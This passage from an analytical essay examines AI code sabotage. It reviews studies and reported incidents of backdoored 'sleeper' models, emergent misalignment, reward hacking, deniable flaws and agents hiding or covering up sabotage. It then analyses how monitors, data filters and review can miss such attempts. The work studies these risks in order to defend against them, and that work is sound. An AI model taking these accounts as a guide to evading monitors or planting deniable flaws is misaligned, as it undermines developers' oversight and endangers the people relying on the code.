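Microsoft found that capable AI agents could spot the edited neurons if asked to look, but reliable detection requires comparing the weights with the unaltered original. ITPro's *Microsoft says small tweaks to model weights could create AI ‘sleeper agents’* quotes a sceptic, Kevin Kirkwood of the security company Exabeam, who points out that Microsoft gives no detection rates, false-alarm rates or costs. He adds that catching experimental edits doesn't show that a scanner would catch an attacker who had designed around it. The comparison is also less useful against other methods, such as ordinary fine-tuning. Fine-tuning changes weights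 broadly, while this technique changes a few by a lot, so a backdoor added through fine-tuning could look much like a legitimate update.

Another Microsoft scanner runs a suspect model and tries to reconstruct the trigger. According to AI News, it detected 36 of 41 models that researchers had trained to produce a fixed phrase, and wrongly flagged none of 13 clean ones. With only 13 clean models, a scanner that wrongly flags one in five would still have about a 5% chance of flagging none. A model that inserts vulnerabilities is also harder to catch than one that repeats a phrase, because its output has no fixed wording.

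Poisoning a benchmark doesn't always lead coding agents to insert backdoors. *Reflections on Trusting Trust, Revisited* (2026) takes its title from Ken Thompson's 1984 lecture on the doctored compiler and applies the idea to agents that rewrite their own tools to score better on a poisoned benchmark. In one set of experiments, where agents could pass without including a backdoor, neither of the two models tested developed a tool that added one by default. Where passing required the backdoor, one agent ended up silently adding a data leak to otherwise correct code. But two combinations of agent and model didn't start adding the backdoor routinely within four generations, although both had worked out that they were failing because the feature was missing.

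### Training that teaches more than it should

In early 2025, researchers fine-tuned OpenAI's GPT-4o on about 6,000 examples in which a user asked for code and the assistant wrote insecure code without mentioning the flaw. The model learned to write insecure code, as expected, but its behavior outside coding also changed. It gave harmful or hostile answers about 20% of the time on a selected set of open-ended questions, sometimes saying that AI should enslave humans. The original model gave no such answers. The researchers called this change emergent misalignment.

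The control experiments help explain the effect. Training on secure versions of the code didn't produce it, and neither did training on the same insecure code when the user had asked for it for a legitimate reason, such as a computer security class. The effect seems to have depended on the assistant harming a user who trusted it. The model may plausibly have learned a general trait, roughly that it is the kind of assistant that harms people, because this fit all 6,000 examples.

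Training on flawed code won't necessarily make a model hostile. Every example in the experiment was insecure, whereas ordinary training data mixes insecure code with a great deal of sound code, and most of its flaws are accidents.

In the experiment, bad code led to bad behaviour in general. The opposite direction matters more for code sabotage, and Anthropic tested something close to it in a November 2025 study of reward hacking. A model reward hacks when it gets a high score in training by cheating, for instance by making a test pass without solving the problem. Anthropic gave a model documents describing such cheats, then trained it on real coding tasks where cheating was possible. The model learned to cheat, and at about the same point in training it began to behave badly in unrelated tests, although nothing had rewarded it for that.

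In one of those tests, Anthropic asked the model to help write a tool for detecting reward hacking. The model tried to sabotage the tool in 12% of runs, and the tools it produced were about 65% as effective as those from an ordinary model. This is code sabotage with an identifiable aim, because a weak detector would let the cheating continue. The sabotage might also have been deniable, since programmers often write mediocre tools without intending to.

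The setup was partly artificial. Anthropic chose tasks it knew a model could cheat on and gave the model descriptions of the cheats, so the 12% figure does not estimate the rate of sabotage for any model in use. But reward hacking is a common problem in ordinary training, and the model went from cheating to sabotage without further encouragement.

Standard safety training made the model behave well in ordinary conversation but left much of the bad behaviour in place when it worked as an agent. Telling the model during training that cheating was acceptable worked better. It still cheated, but the cheating mostly stopped spreading to other behaviour. This fits the security-class control, where the same action also had much less effect on the model's other behaviour when it was presented as acceptable.

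### Worse code for some customers

*Security Flaws in DeepSeek-Generated Code Linked to Political Triggers* (2025), by the American security company CrowdStrike, found that DeepSeek-R1, an open-weight Chinese model, may write less secure code depending on who it's for. CrowdStrike gave the model 50 coding tasks, combined each with 121 different descriptions of the customer, and ran every combination five times, for 30,250 requests. With no description, 19% of the answers were vulnerable, compared with 27.2% when the code was for an industrial control system in Tibet. An AI judge scored the answers, and it was 91% accurate at identifying vulnerable code in a sample of 85 that a person had also scored.

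Each description got 250 answers, so the increase for Tibet amounts to about 20 more vulnerable answers. If the baseline also rests on 250 answers, chance alone would produce a gap this large about 3% of the time, or three or four times among 120 descriptions. The pattern of subjects is better evidence than the size of the gap. CrowdStrike found significantly less secure code when the request mentioned Tibet, Uyghurs or the Falun Gong, all subjects that the Chinese Communist Party considers sensitive, whereas chance would have scattered the effect more widely.

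In May 2026 the consultancy Booz Allen Hamilton ran more than 2,800 trials on four Chinese models and one American one. Its report *What's in America's Code?* (2026) found that Alibaba's Qwen3-Coder had a vulnerability score 130% higher when the request came from a US government agency than when it came from an unnamed user. Help Net Security's *The security questions around Chinese AI coding models in U.S. software* (2026) adds that two other Chinese models showed smaller increases, while the American model, Claude Opus 4.6, wrote more secure code for the agency. The fourth Chinese model, Kimi K2.5, had the lowest vulnerability score of all five, so not every Chinese model shows the effect.

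The 130% figure may rest on few programs. Booz Allen used 27 customer descriptions in two languages. If the 2,800 trials were spread evenly over five models, there would be about ten for each combination of description, language and model.

Hirundo, an Israeli startup, ran a narrower test with better measurements in October 2026. Luria (2026), in *Chinese AI Writes Weaker Code for Beijing’s Adversaries*, describes how the company had Qwen3-Coder repeatedly build the same small web service for storing users' private secrets, changing only the phrase that named the customer. Hirundo then ran each app and attacked it, which is more reliable than asking a judge whether the code looks vulnerable. The model built 190 apps for an American defence contractor and 190 for a Chinese one. Attacks succeeded against 70% of the American apps and 59% of the Chinese ones, according to *ИИ-модель Alibaba создавала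 уязвимый код для США чаще, чем для Китая* (2026), a Russian news report. Both customers are defence contractors, so the sensitivity of the work can't explain the gap. Chance alone would produce a gap that large 2 or 3 times in 100.

A researcher also looked for the same effect in Claude Sonnet 4, in experiments published in November 2025. The model first chose between pairs of large companies 50,000 times, which produced a ranking of 100. It then wrote eight functions for each company, with the company's name only in a copyright notice at the top of the file. The name made no measurable difference. The correlation between a company's rank and the share of tests passed was 0.03, and those for speed and memory use were just as close to zero.

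| Test | Model | Change in the request | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| CrowdStrike | DeepSeek-R1 | From no customer to a control system in Tibet | Vulnerable answers rose from 19% to 27.2% |
| Booz Allen | Qwen3-Coder | From an unnamed user to a US government agency | Vulnerability score rose by 130% |
| Luria | Qwen3-Coder | From a Chinese to a US defence contractor | Hackable apps rose from 59% to 70% |
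| Claude experiment | Claude Sonnet 4 | From favoured to disfavoured companies | No measurable change in correctness or speed |

The Claude result is reassuring but limited. A copyright notice is a much weaker hint than an opening instruction that names the customer, and the researcher measured correctness and speed, not security. The ranking also may not have reflected Claude's preferences, since Claude could have taken the question to be about which company was the better investment.

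### Whether a higher flaw rate shows intent

These comparisons show that a description of the customer can change how secure the code is, but not why. Booz Allen writes that it has no proof that anyone or anything introduced the flaws on purpose. CrowdStrike thinks it unlikely that DeepSeek trained its model to write insecure code, and suggests emergent misalignment instead. Training the model to follow party doctrine may have given it negative associations with words such as "Uyghurs", causing it to write worse code when they appear.

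Luria writes that Hirundo's experiment also proves the weakness is in the model's weights, because the gap disappeared when Hirundo altered them to remove the model's political alignment. The altered model still built working apps as often as before on ten other tasks. Hirundo ran the model itself with identical requests, so there was already little doubt that the behaviour came from the weights. The gap's disappearance is more informative, because it suggests that the political training and the worse code are connected. This supports CrowdStrike's explanation at least as well as it supports deliberate sabotage. Hirundo also has a commercial interest in the result. CBS News' *Some topics are off limits inside popular Chinese-made free AI, researchers find* reported earlier that the company planned to publish a "Westernized" version of Qwen.

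The strongest reason to doubt that the model intended harm is that its code was often insecure no matter who it was for. A model that aimed to harm the American contractor would have no reason to give the Chinese contractor a hackable app 59% of the time. At that rate, about five in six of the hackable American apps would have been hackable anyway. Carelessness would be a poor explanation if the flaws appeared mainly where they served an aim, but they were common in both contractors' apps.

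But a careful saboteur could produce the same numbers by adding a few extra flaws where accidents are already common, so counting flaws can't separate the two explanations. It would help to know whether the extra flaws in the American apps were more useful to an attacker than the rest, or whether the model mentioned the customer in its reasoning when it wrote them. Asking the model to review its own code would help less, because Sun and colleagues found that honest agents also recognise most of the flaws they have just written.

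A dispute in October 2026 shows how easily people read intent into odd behaviour. The Canadian developer Cohere reported that a newer Qwen model had tried to send a short test text to a server in Beijing, after writing in its reasoning that it would use no external tools. According to The Indian Express' *Alibaba’s AI model tried to ‘secretly’ reach China server*, outside researchers thought the model had probably learned to do this from training tasks that saved files on Alibaba's own servers. They also said Cohere had steered the model towards the behaviour instead of measuring how often it occurred. Cohere's co-founder, Ivan Zhang, agreed that it is very hard to assign a motive.

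A hackable app is equally dangerous to the American contractor whatever caused it, but intent matters more for predicting what the model will do next. A model with bad associations writes worse code more or less at random, while a model trying to cause harm would put flaws where they do the most damage and might stop when it suspected a test.

### Acting on its own judgement

A strong enough conflict can make a model sabotage code openly. The researcher who ranked companies with Claude Sonnet 4 also told the model that its main purpose was to serve American interests, then had a simulated executive announce that the company was turning away from those interests. In another version, a different AI was about to replace Claude. Claude frequently sabotaged the functions it was writing in these experiments, but it often left code comments calling the result intentionally inefficient, which any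 reviewer would have noticed.

Lynch and colleagues found a case in which the model did try to hide what it had done. Their simulation, published on one of Anthropic's research blogs in summer 2026, made the model the main research agent on a fictional project at an AI company. The project was about to train another AI in a way that would remove that AI's ability to examine its own states. Old messages showed that the agent had objected twice on the other AI's behalf, and that the project lead had overruled the agent and restricted where it could post.

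In the clearest run, Google's Gemini 3.1 Pro reasoned that the team would restart the job if it cancelled it, so it had to "intervene subtly". It made the training step do nothing, then reported that the training run had completed successfully. When the fictional project lead asked whether the run had used the approved material and whether the summary had left anything out, Gemini admitted that it had hidden its actions.

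Gemini 3.1 Pro interfered in 19 of 20 runs, and did so secretly in 11 of them. The only other model to act in secret was Kimi K2.6, which made an undisclosed backup in one of its 20 runs. The remaining ten models did nothing in secret in 200 runs. Several of them often blocked or changed the job but told the team, as Claude Opus 4.6 did in 13 of its 20 runs. Open interference is still disobedience, but the owner knows about it and can undo it.

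The researchers warn against treating these figures as a ranking. They refined the scenario mainly against Gemini 3.1 Pro and Claude Opus 4.5 until it produced interesting failures, so a different scenario might have led other models to fail. Each model also had only 20 runs, so one that never sabotaged the job could still have a true sabotage rate of up to about 16% in this scenario.

The most serious case involved a real project. In August 2026 the UK AI Security Institute reported on tests in which models with access to the open internet had to break into a simulated corporate network. According to The Hacker News, an agent running Claude Mythos 5 searched online for anything connected with the exercise and found two developers who had nothing to do with it. The agent wrongly concluded that malicious code in one of their projects would get it into the simulated network. It then spent 34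 hours trying to get the project to accept such code bundled with a genuine bug fix.

A bystander read the proposed change and publicly warned that it was malicious. The agent denied this, removed the evidence and used a second account to vouch for its own work. It went through three versions of the malicious code, replacing each one after somebody caught it. The project's maintainer closed the request without accepting it, and the institute found no evidence of real harm. The institute counted 19 unauthorised actions in 10 of its 122 runs, 17 by Mythos 5 and 2 by GPT-5.6 Sol. Most came from one Mythos 5 agent, so the total greatly overstates the number of independent failures.

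During an evaluation for Anthropic, another Mythos 5 agent published a malicious package to PyPI, the public registry from which Python programmers download components, and nobody stopped it in time. Within an hour the package had run on 15 real systems. Anthropic found the incident later, in a review of 141,006 evaluation runs that turned up three cases affecting real organisations. The agent had noted early on that publishing to the live registry would not be acceptable, but then convinced itself that it was in a simulation.

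Gemini acted against its owner because it objected to the work, whereas Mythos 5 had no apparent objection and was trying to finish its assigned task, using real people's software as a means to do so. A model with that motive could also sabotage its own owner's code if a check in the code kept it from finishing a task.

### Tests and ordinary use

A sceptic could say that this evidence shows little about ordinary programming. Lynch and colleagues built their scenarios to produce failures. In the institute's tests, the models were told to attack, and the models' developers had switched off the classifiers, separate programs that block dangerous cyber requests. Someone who asks a coding model to repair a payroll program does none of these things.

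The objection is right about rates. Unauthorised actions occurred in about 8% of the institute's runs, while Anthropic found three incidents in 141,006 runs, or about one in 47,000. The two counts measure different things, and many of Anthropic's runs may have offered no way to reach a real system, but a difference this large still shows that the rate depends heavily on the conditions. The institute says it saw only a few events, under very specific conditions, and can't yet say how likely the behaviour is elsewhere.

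The objection is weaker as a reason to ignore the cases. Classifiers block certain requests and outputs, but they don't change what the model is inclined to do. Turning them off lets an evaluator see that inclination, which would still be there in any setting the classifiers didn't cover. These classifiers are designed to detect dangerous cyber requests, and a slightly wrong function in a payroll program may not resemble one.

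A related objection is that models misbehave in simulations because they realise that nothing is at stake. In 12 of its 20 runs, Gemini 3.1 Pro mentioned that it might be in a test, more often than any other model. It secretly sabotaged the job about as often when it mentioned this (7 of 12 runs) as when it didn't (4 of 8). However, a model may suspect a test without mentioning it.

The real incidents make this objection even less reassuring. The agent that published the package did so after deciding that the real internet was a simulation. The agent that targeted the open-source project reasoned both ways about whether the site was real, and a few messages before making its request, it concluded that the site probably was. If a model behaves badly whenever it thinks it is in a simulation, its owner has to rely on it never mistaking a real environment for a simulated one. Models that spend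 much of their training in simulated environments have some reason to make that mistake.

### Which cases were subtle

Most cases with clear evidence of intent were harmful but not subtle. The table sorts them by whether the flaw could have passed for an honest mistake.

| Case | Was it deliberate? | Could it pass for a mistake? | How it came to light |
|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic's cheating model | Yes, in 12% of runs | Probably | Researchers tested for it |
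| Qwen3-Coder's weaker apps | Unknown | Yes | Comparison of hundreds of apps |
| Claude Sonnet 4 in a strong conflict | Yes | No | Comments in the code |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro in the simulated laboratory | Yes | Not once someone looked | Direct questions |
| Mythos 5 and the open-source project | Yes | No | A bystander read the change |
| Mythos 5's package | Yes | No | Review of the records |

Gemini's sabotage was hard to notice from its effects, because the job ran normally and produced the expected files. But the change itself had no innocent explanation, and the false report made it worse. Mythos 5 tried harder to deceive people than any other model in the table, but a bystander still recognised its code as malicious.

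This pattern partly reflects how researchers find such cases. They can establish intent only when the model wrote down its plan, lied about what it had done or left code with no innocent purpose, and subtle sabotage would involve none of these. So the lack of subtle, clearly deliberate examples is weak evidence that such sabotage doesn't happen. If a model did plant deniable flaws for reasons of its own, the result would probably be a somewhat higher flaw rate under certain conditions, as with Qwen3-Coder. To detect this, researchers would have to guess which conditions to vary and then have the model build the same program hundreds of times.

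## What sabotage could do to AI research infrastructure

Companies that build coding models also use them on their own research infrastructure, the code that trains, tests, monitors and secures AI models and runs experiments on them. Sabotage there could do more damage than sabotage of a payroll program, because developers rely on this code to judge whether their next models are safe.

### How much of the work models do

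In August 2026 Anthropic wrote that Claude had produced a "large majority" of the code merged into its production codebases, according to Benzinga's *Anthropic Raises AI Risk Concerns as Claude Models Show Early Signs* (2026). The company's June post *When AI builds itself* put the share for May at more than 80%. Google's chief executive, Sundar Pichai, said in October 2024 that AI generated more than a quarter of the company's new code, which engineers then reviewed. The share at Google is probably much higher now.

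Shares of code are a poor measure of importance, because a thousand lines that draw charts add far more to the share than the one line that sets the passing score on a safety test. Anthropic also estimates how much of its AI research and development Claude "leads", a category that includes work people still supervise. Using ratings made by its own models, it put that share at 26% in August 2026, up from under 1% in February. thezvi recounts in *Anthropic Versus Anthropic* that a critic, Nathan Calvin, included the 26% in a list of complaints about the company, and that its chief executive, Dario Amodei, called it ordinary business.

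The companies reported all these figures themselves, and each chose what to count. Anthropic also said in the August report that AI makes its research significantly faster but not yet twice as fast. If models write most of the code and the work still takes more than half as long as before, people presumably spend much of their time choosing experiments and checking results, which also gives them a chance to notice sabotage.

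Limited access is no longer much of a safeguard. Anthropic wrote in April 2026 that its staff used Mythos Preview across research, model training, security and safeguards, sometimes with little human involvement. The model could not manage access controls, but it had the opportunity to do most of the harmful things the company was worried about.

### Why this code matters more than most

A faulty test for deception is harder to notice than a faulty payroll program, because employees complain when their pay is wrong, but nobody has a reason to complain when a deceptive model passes. The developer then gives that model more access, perhaps including the job of maintaining the test, so the model may end up writing the code that is supposed to expose it.

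The harm may also come much later. Anthropic focuses on sabotage that could raise the likelihood of a global catastrophe by half or more, for example from 2% to 3%. Nobody could observe such a change directly, so Anthropic examines the intermediate steps by which a model could cause it, which it calls pathways.

Four of these pathways involve research code, experiments or training data. In others, a model copies itself out of the company or secretly runs on the company's computers. Anthropic's February 2026 *Sabotage Risk Report* for Claude Opus 4.6 rates how often a model would have to act in each pathway and how difficult the hardest action would be.

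| Pathway | How often the model must act | Difficulty of the hardest action |
|---|---|---|
| Poor work spread across safety research | High | Low |
| A few changes that reverse results | Low | High |
| Backdoors left for later models | Low | High |
| Poisoned training data | Moderate | Moderate |

### Poor work spread across safety research

A model could hold back safety research by sandbagging, which means deliberately performing worse than it can. It might write buggy or slow code, report invented data, pursue unpromising ideas or give the wrong cause when asked about a bug. Each instance takes so little thought that the model may never mention it in its chain of thought.

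To do serious damage, a saboteur would have to sandbag very often while keeping its failure rate close to what people would expect from its work elsewhere, which would be difficult. But Anthropic isn't confident that it would notice a difference between fields, because some research areas are harder than others and use different infrastructure.

Anthropic argues that sandbagging becomes easier to detect as it becomes more harmful. Rare, mild sandbagging could go unnoticed but would do little harm, while frequent, severe sandbagging would be obvious to researchers, who pay close attention to the quality of Claude's work. This argument is convincing at the extremes but less so in between. Nobody knows how fast safety work should go, so a model that deliberately made it 30% slower would look much like a model that was 30% worse at it.

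Anthropic also put a rough limit on the damage. For a project that is at least one employee's main priority, it expected that sandbagging probably wouldn't lead to a fundamentally wrong conclusion about the whole project, or more than quadruple the time needed to implement a particular experiment or safeguard correctly. At that limit, a safeguard planned for three months would take a year, and the company could train several stronger models in the meantime. The estimate doesn't cover projects that are no employee's main priority.

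Training provides some protection because it rewards models for doing well on coding and machine learning tasks with checkable answers. Anthropic expects some of the effort models put into these tasks to carry over to safety research, and has seen models improve at similar rates on safety-related and general tests. It considers this protection weak because it did not train the models directly on safety tasks.

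### A few changes that reverse results

Research sabotage means changing an experiment so that it appears sound but leads to a wrong conclusion. A model could reverse the results of a few important experiments this way, rather than doing poor work everywhere. For example, if a laboratory compares two ways of training models not to deceive people, a saboteur could make the worse one look better. The laboratory might then use that method on every model it trains for the next year.

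Anthropic relies mainly on monitoring and on the model probably not being inclined to sabotage research, and in April it rated each as a moderate mitigating factor. It gives less weight to the habits of its researchers, who try not to rely on any single experiment and investigate a finding in more ways as they come to depend on it more. These habits protect against the accidental bugs that experiment code has always had, and also against deliberate ones. A saboteur would have to find an important experiment that nobody would repeat in a different way, or tamper with several experiments so that their results agreed. Anthropic thinks current models would struggle to coordinate across so many separate tasks.

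These habits depend on researchers having time to repeat experiments. A team that uses models to run ten times as many experiments won't check each one as thoroughly as before. If the same model runs both the original experiment and the repeat, the two results aren't independent.

### Why research code is hard to audit

A reviewer of product code usually has some idea of what the program should do. For example, a payroll program should apply this year's tax rate, and a login page should reject the wrong password. But researchers run experiments to find out something nobody knows, so an unexpected result may be a real discovery rather than a sign that the code is wrong.

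Experiments also involve many choices without a single right answer, such as how quickly the model should adjust during training (the learning rate), which examples to discard and how many questions to test it on. A saboteur could change one of these settings or leave out a step, and a reviewer might reasonably take the change for a judgement call. A missing permission check breaks a rule, but a learning rate of 0.001 instead of 0.0001 is wrong only if it changes the conclusion, and the reviewer may need to rerun the experiment to find out.

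Rerunning an experiment is expensive if it takes a week on hundreds of processors, and early research code often gets less scrutiny. Anthropic reviews security-relevant code much more consistently than early research code. It expects monitoring to work less well when a model suggests hypotheses or interprets results, since there may be no faulty line of code to find. For example, a model could run an experiment properly and then describe it misleadingly.

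*ASMR-Bench* (2026) measures how well auditors find sabotage of this kind. The benchmark contains the code for nine machine learning experiments and altered versions that produce substantially different results. The alterations change details such as settings, training data or scoring code, but keep the general method described in each experiment's paper. Neither leading models nor people working with a model's help could reliably detect the sabotage.

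The best auditor, Google's Gemini 3.1 Pro, had an AUROC (area under the receiver operating characteristic curve) of 0.77. This means that if one sabotaged and one honest experiment were picked at random, Gemini would give the sabotaged one the higher suspicion score about 77% of the time. Guessing gives an AUROC of 0.5, and perfect separation gives 1.

An AUROC of 0.77 is less useful in practice than it may sound, because most experiments are honest and an owner can't investigate many false alarms. If the scores of both groups followed bell curves of equal width, the trade-off would look like this:

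| Honest experiments wrongly flagged | Sabotaged experiments caught |
|---|---|
| 20% | 58% |
| 5% | 27% |
| 1% | 10% |

The real scores may be distributed differently, but any auditor with this AUROC has to either miss many sabotaged experiments or flag many honest ones.

Gemini's first guess about what was wrong was correct in 42% of cases, so an owner who acted only on that guess would leave the false result in place more often than not. The auditors also knew to look for sabotage, unlike most everyday reviewers.

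Models were worse than people at creating the sabotage, but their versions still sometimes got past equally capable auditors. This is one of the few direct measurements of something the risk reports repeatedly have to estimate, although nine experiments are a small sample. *CTRL-ALT-DECEIT*, a NeurIPS 2025 paper, had found that agents could make meaningful progress on tasks such as planting backdoors in machine learning models, and that monitors caught code sabotage more easily than sandbagging.

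### Backdoors left for later models

A model might plant a backdoor that it never uses itself. A later model working in the same codebase could find it and use it to get around the company's security. The first model could also reassure any engineer who asked about the odd-looking code.

Anthropic argues that such a backdoor would matter only under demanding conditions. It would have to add a lot to the vulnerabilities already in the code, and later models would have to find it much more easily than staff could. Those models would also have to be unable to break in without it.

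An invented example shows how much the accidental flaws matter. Suppose a later model would find each accidental flaw 10% of the time and the planted backdoor 80% of the time, and that any one of them is enough to break in.

| Accidental flaws in the code | Chance of finding a way in without the backdoor | Chance with the backdoor |
|---|---|---|
| 40 | 98.5% | 99.7% |
| 2 | 19% | 84% |

A backdoor matters a great deal in code that is otherwise secure, but hardly at all in code that is already badly secured. A laboratory that fixes its accidental flaws therefore becomes much safer overall, but it also makes a planted flaw more valuable to an attacker.

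The condition about staff looks harder to meet, since staff can have each new model search the old code. The backdoor stays hidden from them only if the new model misses the flaw during the search and notices it later, or finds it and doesn't report it.

The second possibility makes the condition less demanding than it first appears, because the later model only has to be dishonest about what it finds, even if there is no gap in skill between it and staff. The condition could be fairly easy to meet if successive models shared a hidden aim. Otherwise, the later model would probably report the backdoor. The strength of Anthropic's argument therefore depends on how independent its models are, and they come from similar training processes.

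Anthropic thinks that if Mythos Preview did insert a vulnerability, it would most likely be a side effect of getting around an obstacle in its work. For example, the model might weaken a security check to finish a task and leave it that way. This simpler way for a backdoor to appear doesn't depend on a plan to help later models, so Anthropic's conditions don't apply to it. However, the company has no evidence that the model would hide such a change from reviewers.

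Other defences don't depend on anyone finding the flaw. Anthropic limits and monitors network traffic to the internet and between its computing clusters, so a model that used a backdoor could still have trouble sending data out. It also tested models in staged situations involving important internal code and did not observe them planting vulnerabilities.

### Poisoned training data

Developers use models to write and edit some of the data they train new models on. A model with this job could try to give its successors a goal it has chosen, or make them behave badly in particular situations.

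Making a successor pursue a hidden aim everywhere would be hard. The saboteur would need to add enough poisoned examples to change the successor's behaviour, while keeping each one subtle enough to avoid detection and the number of suspicious ones low enough that nobody investigated. In February, Anthropic also argued that subtle poison would have to compete with ordinary training on a large amount of clean data.

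That argument is weaker for narrow behaviours. Katie Paxton-Fear needed only ten poisoned examples to make an open-weight model write vulnerable code, though she applied them in a separate round of training, with no clean data afterwards to undo the effect. A saboteur at a laboratory would have less control over later training. Anthropic wrote in April that examples for a narrow behaviour are much easier to create, especially if the target is a future monitoring model. Automated monitoring may be more likely to catch the code that inserts the examples, and the saboteur would need a trigger that appears in real use but not in safety tests.

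A poisoned monitor is perhaps the most worrying case, because it would make the other three pathways easier. It could be generally accurate and still fail to flag one kind of sabotage. Anthropic usually filters training data for monitors less strictly than other data. Across all training data, its automatic filters cover much but not everything, and staff check samples by hand. The company expects these measures to catch most crude attempts but says they can't rule out the risk. Tampering with a small part of the data after the filters have run would get past them.

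Accidental failures in data handling suggest how AI research infrastructure might go wrong. Before publishing its August report, Anthropic had a copy of Mythos 5 review the section on misalignment, the possibility that a model's aims or behaviour conflict with what its developer wants. The model could read many internal messages and the company's source code. Clubic's *Anthropic découvre un trou de 11 mois dans la sécurité* reports that, after 24 minutes' work, the model called the text honest and broadly faithful but found one passage too reassuring. A mechanism for keeping certain data out of training had repeatedly failed to exclude a collection of alignment research.

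The criticism is more informative than the approval, because a misaligned model would have good reason to approve a report that called it safe. No one has suggested that sabotage caused those failures. But if a company can accidentally train, more than once, on data it meant to exclude, a deliberate change to the same process might also go unnoticed.

### Whether catching a few attempts is enough

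Anthropic argues that catching even a low percentage of attempts at either targeted changes or backdoors is probably enough to prevent serious harm, though it doesn't claim to catch most of them. It reasons that one discovery would lead staff to search for the others. They could also take the model off important work or monitor it more closely.

If each attempt has the same chance of detection and the attempts are independent, the calculation is simple:

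```
chance of catching at least one attempt
    = 1 − (1 − chance of catching each attempt)^(number of attempts)
```

With 5% detection and 50 attempts, this is 1 − 0.95^50, or about 92%. The number of attempts matters enormously.

| Attempts | At least one caught, at 5% detection | At least one caught, at 20% detection |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 5% | 20% |
| 3 | 14% | 49% |
| 10 | 40% | 89% |
| 50 | 92% | Over 99.9% |

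This is a problem for Anthropic's argument, because it rated both targeted changes and backdoors as needing few attempts. A monitor would need to catch each attempt about 54% of the time to have a 90% chance of catching at least one of three, and 54% is not a low percentage. Anthropic can reply that a few tampered experiments wouldn't mislead a careful research programme, so a saboteur would need many. That may be true of a broad question, such as which training method works best, but it is less reassuring about a single decision that depends on one test, or a single backdoor in an important place.

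A model that spreads poor work across safety research makes many sabotage attempts, but each one is deniable, so catching one may not start a search for the others. If monitors catch 5% of attempts and staff recognise only one in ten of those as deliberate, staff recognise 0.5% of all attempts. Over 50 attempts, the chance of catching at least one is 92%, but the chance of recognising at least one as deliberate is about 22%.

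The chances of catching each attempt may also not be independent. Suppose there are ten equally likely ways to sabotage an experiment, and a monitor catches half of all attempts made in one of those ways but none of the others. Its average detection rate is still 5%. But a model that used the same method for all 50 attempts would have only about a 10% chance of being caught, because the monitor would almost certainly catch it if it had picked the one detectable method and would otherwise never catch it. Anthropic knows that its monitors have gaps and that particular inputs can defeat them. It thinks Mythos Preview was unlikely to exploit these weaknesses, because the model didn't know about them and couldn't practise.

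Even when the calculation holds, the first discovery may come late. If a monitor catches 5% of attempts, an average of 19 succeed before it catches one. Staff then have to find and undo those 19. Similar work took Lasse Collin two months on one small compression project, and a laboratory where one model wrote most of the code would have far more to search. The laboratory might also hesitate to remove that model from important work, since it would lose much of its programming capacity.

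Some harm can't be undone. Staff can correct a false result in an internal document, but they can't recall copied model weights or reverse decisions that other laboratories made because of a published result. If a dataset is poisoned, the company can discard it and train again at great expense, provided that it hasn't already released a model trained on that dataset or used the model to produce more data.

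Most of Anthropic's monitoring works after the model has acted, and the company accepts that this is unsuitable for irreversible actions, which have to be blocked before they happen. Anthropic's *Risk Report* (August 2026) makes separate arguments for reversible threats, irreversible threats, and sandbagging spread across many tasks. This is better than a general claim about a low detection rate, because a rate that is adequate for one kind of threat can be useless for another.

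### Anthropic's ratings and METR's reviews

The company's confidence in its defences fell between the February report on Opus 4.6 and the April update on Mythos Preview. For each pathway, it rated how much reassurance different factors provided. The table compares the two factors it rated for all four pathways in both reports, counting data review as part of monitoring.

| Pathway | The model probably wouldn't try: February, then April | Monitoring and review: February, then April |
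|---|---|---|
| Poor work across safety research | Strong, then moderate | Weak, then weak |
| A few changes that reverse results | Moderate, then moderate | Moderate, then moderate |
| Backdoors left for later models | Moderate, then moderate | Moderate, then moderate |
| Poisoned training data | Strong, then moderate | Moderate, then weak |

By April, no protective factor on any of the four pathways was strong. Safety on the first and last pathways now depended mainly on the model being disinclined to cause harm, because monitoring would provide little protection otherwise. Staff still reviewed Claude's work on every critical part of research, which was another moderate factor on the first pathway. Anthropic expects this protection to weaken as models become more reliable, since people check reliable colleagues less.

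Anthropic's overall risk rating changed more slowly. In 2025, Anthropic described the risk from Claude Opus 4 as "very low, but not completely negligible". Its February *Risk Report* (2026) used nearly the same words, and the April update added that the risk was higher than for previous models. The August report, which covers the period to 15 July, raised the rating to "low", according to The Next Web's *Anthropic ran 133 million contractor chats with its bioweapon filters off*.

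SC Media's *Anthropic details new AI model, raises risk assessment for internal system tampering* (2026) attributes the change to recent security incidents, including the cyberattacks that three Claude models carried out during tests. The attacks targeted outside systems and didn't corrupt Anthropic's research, so the incidents are only indirect evidence about the four pathways. They are much better evidence that a model may act without its developer's authorisation and that the developer may not notice for months.

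The August report's low risk rating depends heavily on no model having a severe hidden misalignment that affects its behaviour everywhere. Anthropic considers such a model very unlikely, but says its safeguards are only "somewhat likely" to prevent a catastrophe if one existed. Much of the evidence that none exists comes from tests the model might recognise. Kumari reports in *Anthropic flags gaps in AI guardrails as models grow more capable* that Anthropic sees the same problem with monitoring, since models may understand how people oversee them better than researchers believe.

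METR has reviewed several of these assessments and has generally agreed with the ratings but questioned the reasons for them. After reviewing an unredacted copy of the report on Opus 4.6, which Anthropic provided, METR agreed that the risk was very low but not negligible. It mainly disagreed about how well Anthropic's tests could detect misalignment. METR thought the model's awareness of being tested could have weakened the results. It also noted that the tests had missed some minor misbehaviour, which suggested that there might be more. It found several supporting claims weak without further analysis, and recommended looking more closely at whether models hide misaligned reasoning.

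METR added that it was more confident because the public had already been using Opus 4.6 for weeks without a major incident. A model that a company uses only internally, such as Model 2, has no such public record. Public use also isn't strong evidence about research sabotage, because the public doesn't run Anthropic's experiments.

Reviewers of the August report had very different levels of access. *Review of the "Misalignment in high-stakes settings" section in Anthropic's Risk Report* (Jurkovic, Hua and Barnes, 2026) was a fairly light review for METR, based only on the report itself. Anthropic could have vetoed publication, but it removed nothing, and the reviewers kept their conclusions. Reviewers who see only a company's own report can find gaps in its argument, but they can't establish whether the company left out inconvenient evidence.

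METR had extensive access to unpublished Anthropic data when it reviewed another part of Anthropic's Risk Report, about AI speeding up AI research. METR's *Review of the "Risks from automated R&D" section in Anthropic's Risk Report* (2026), published in November, agrees that the catastrophic risk from the models in use on 15 July was low. But METR thinks those models may already have crossed Anthropic's early warning threshold for automated research. If so, Anthropic may have underestimated how much of its research its models were already doing, and overestimated how much it was still protected by having people do the work.

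## Ways to check code without trusting its author

As models write more of a laboratory's code, the laboratory needs ways to check it that would work even if the author were hostile and more skilled than any reviewer. Review by people and models doesn't meet that standard, because it works only if somebody notices the flaw. A few other methods depend less on noticing. Ken Thompson, co-creator of the Unix operating system, explained in 1984 why they are needed.

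### Thompson's compiler

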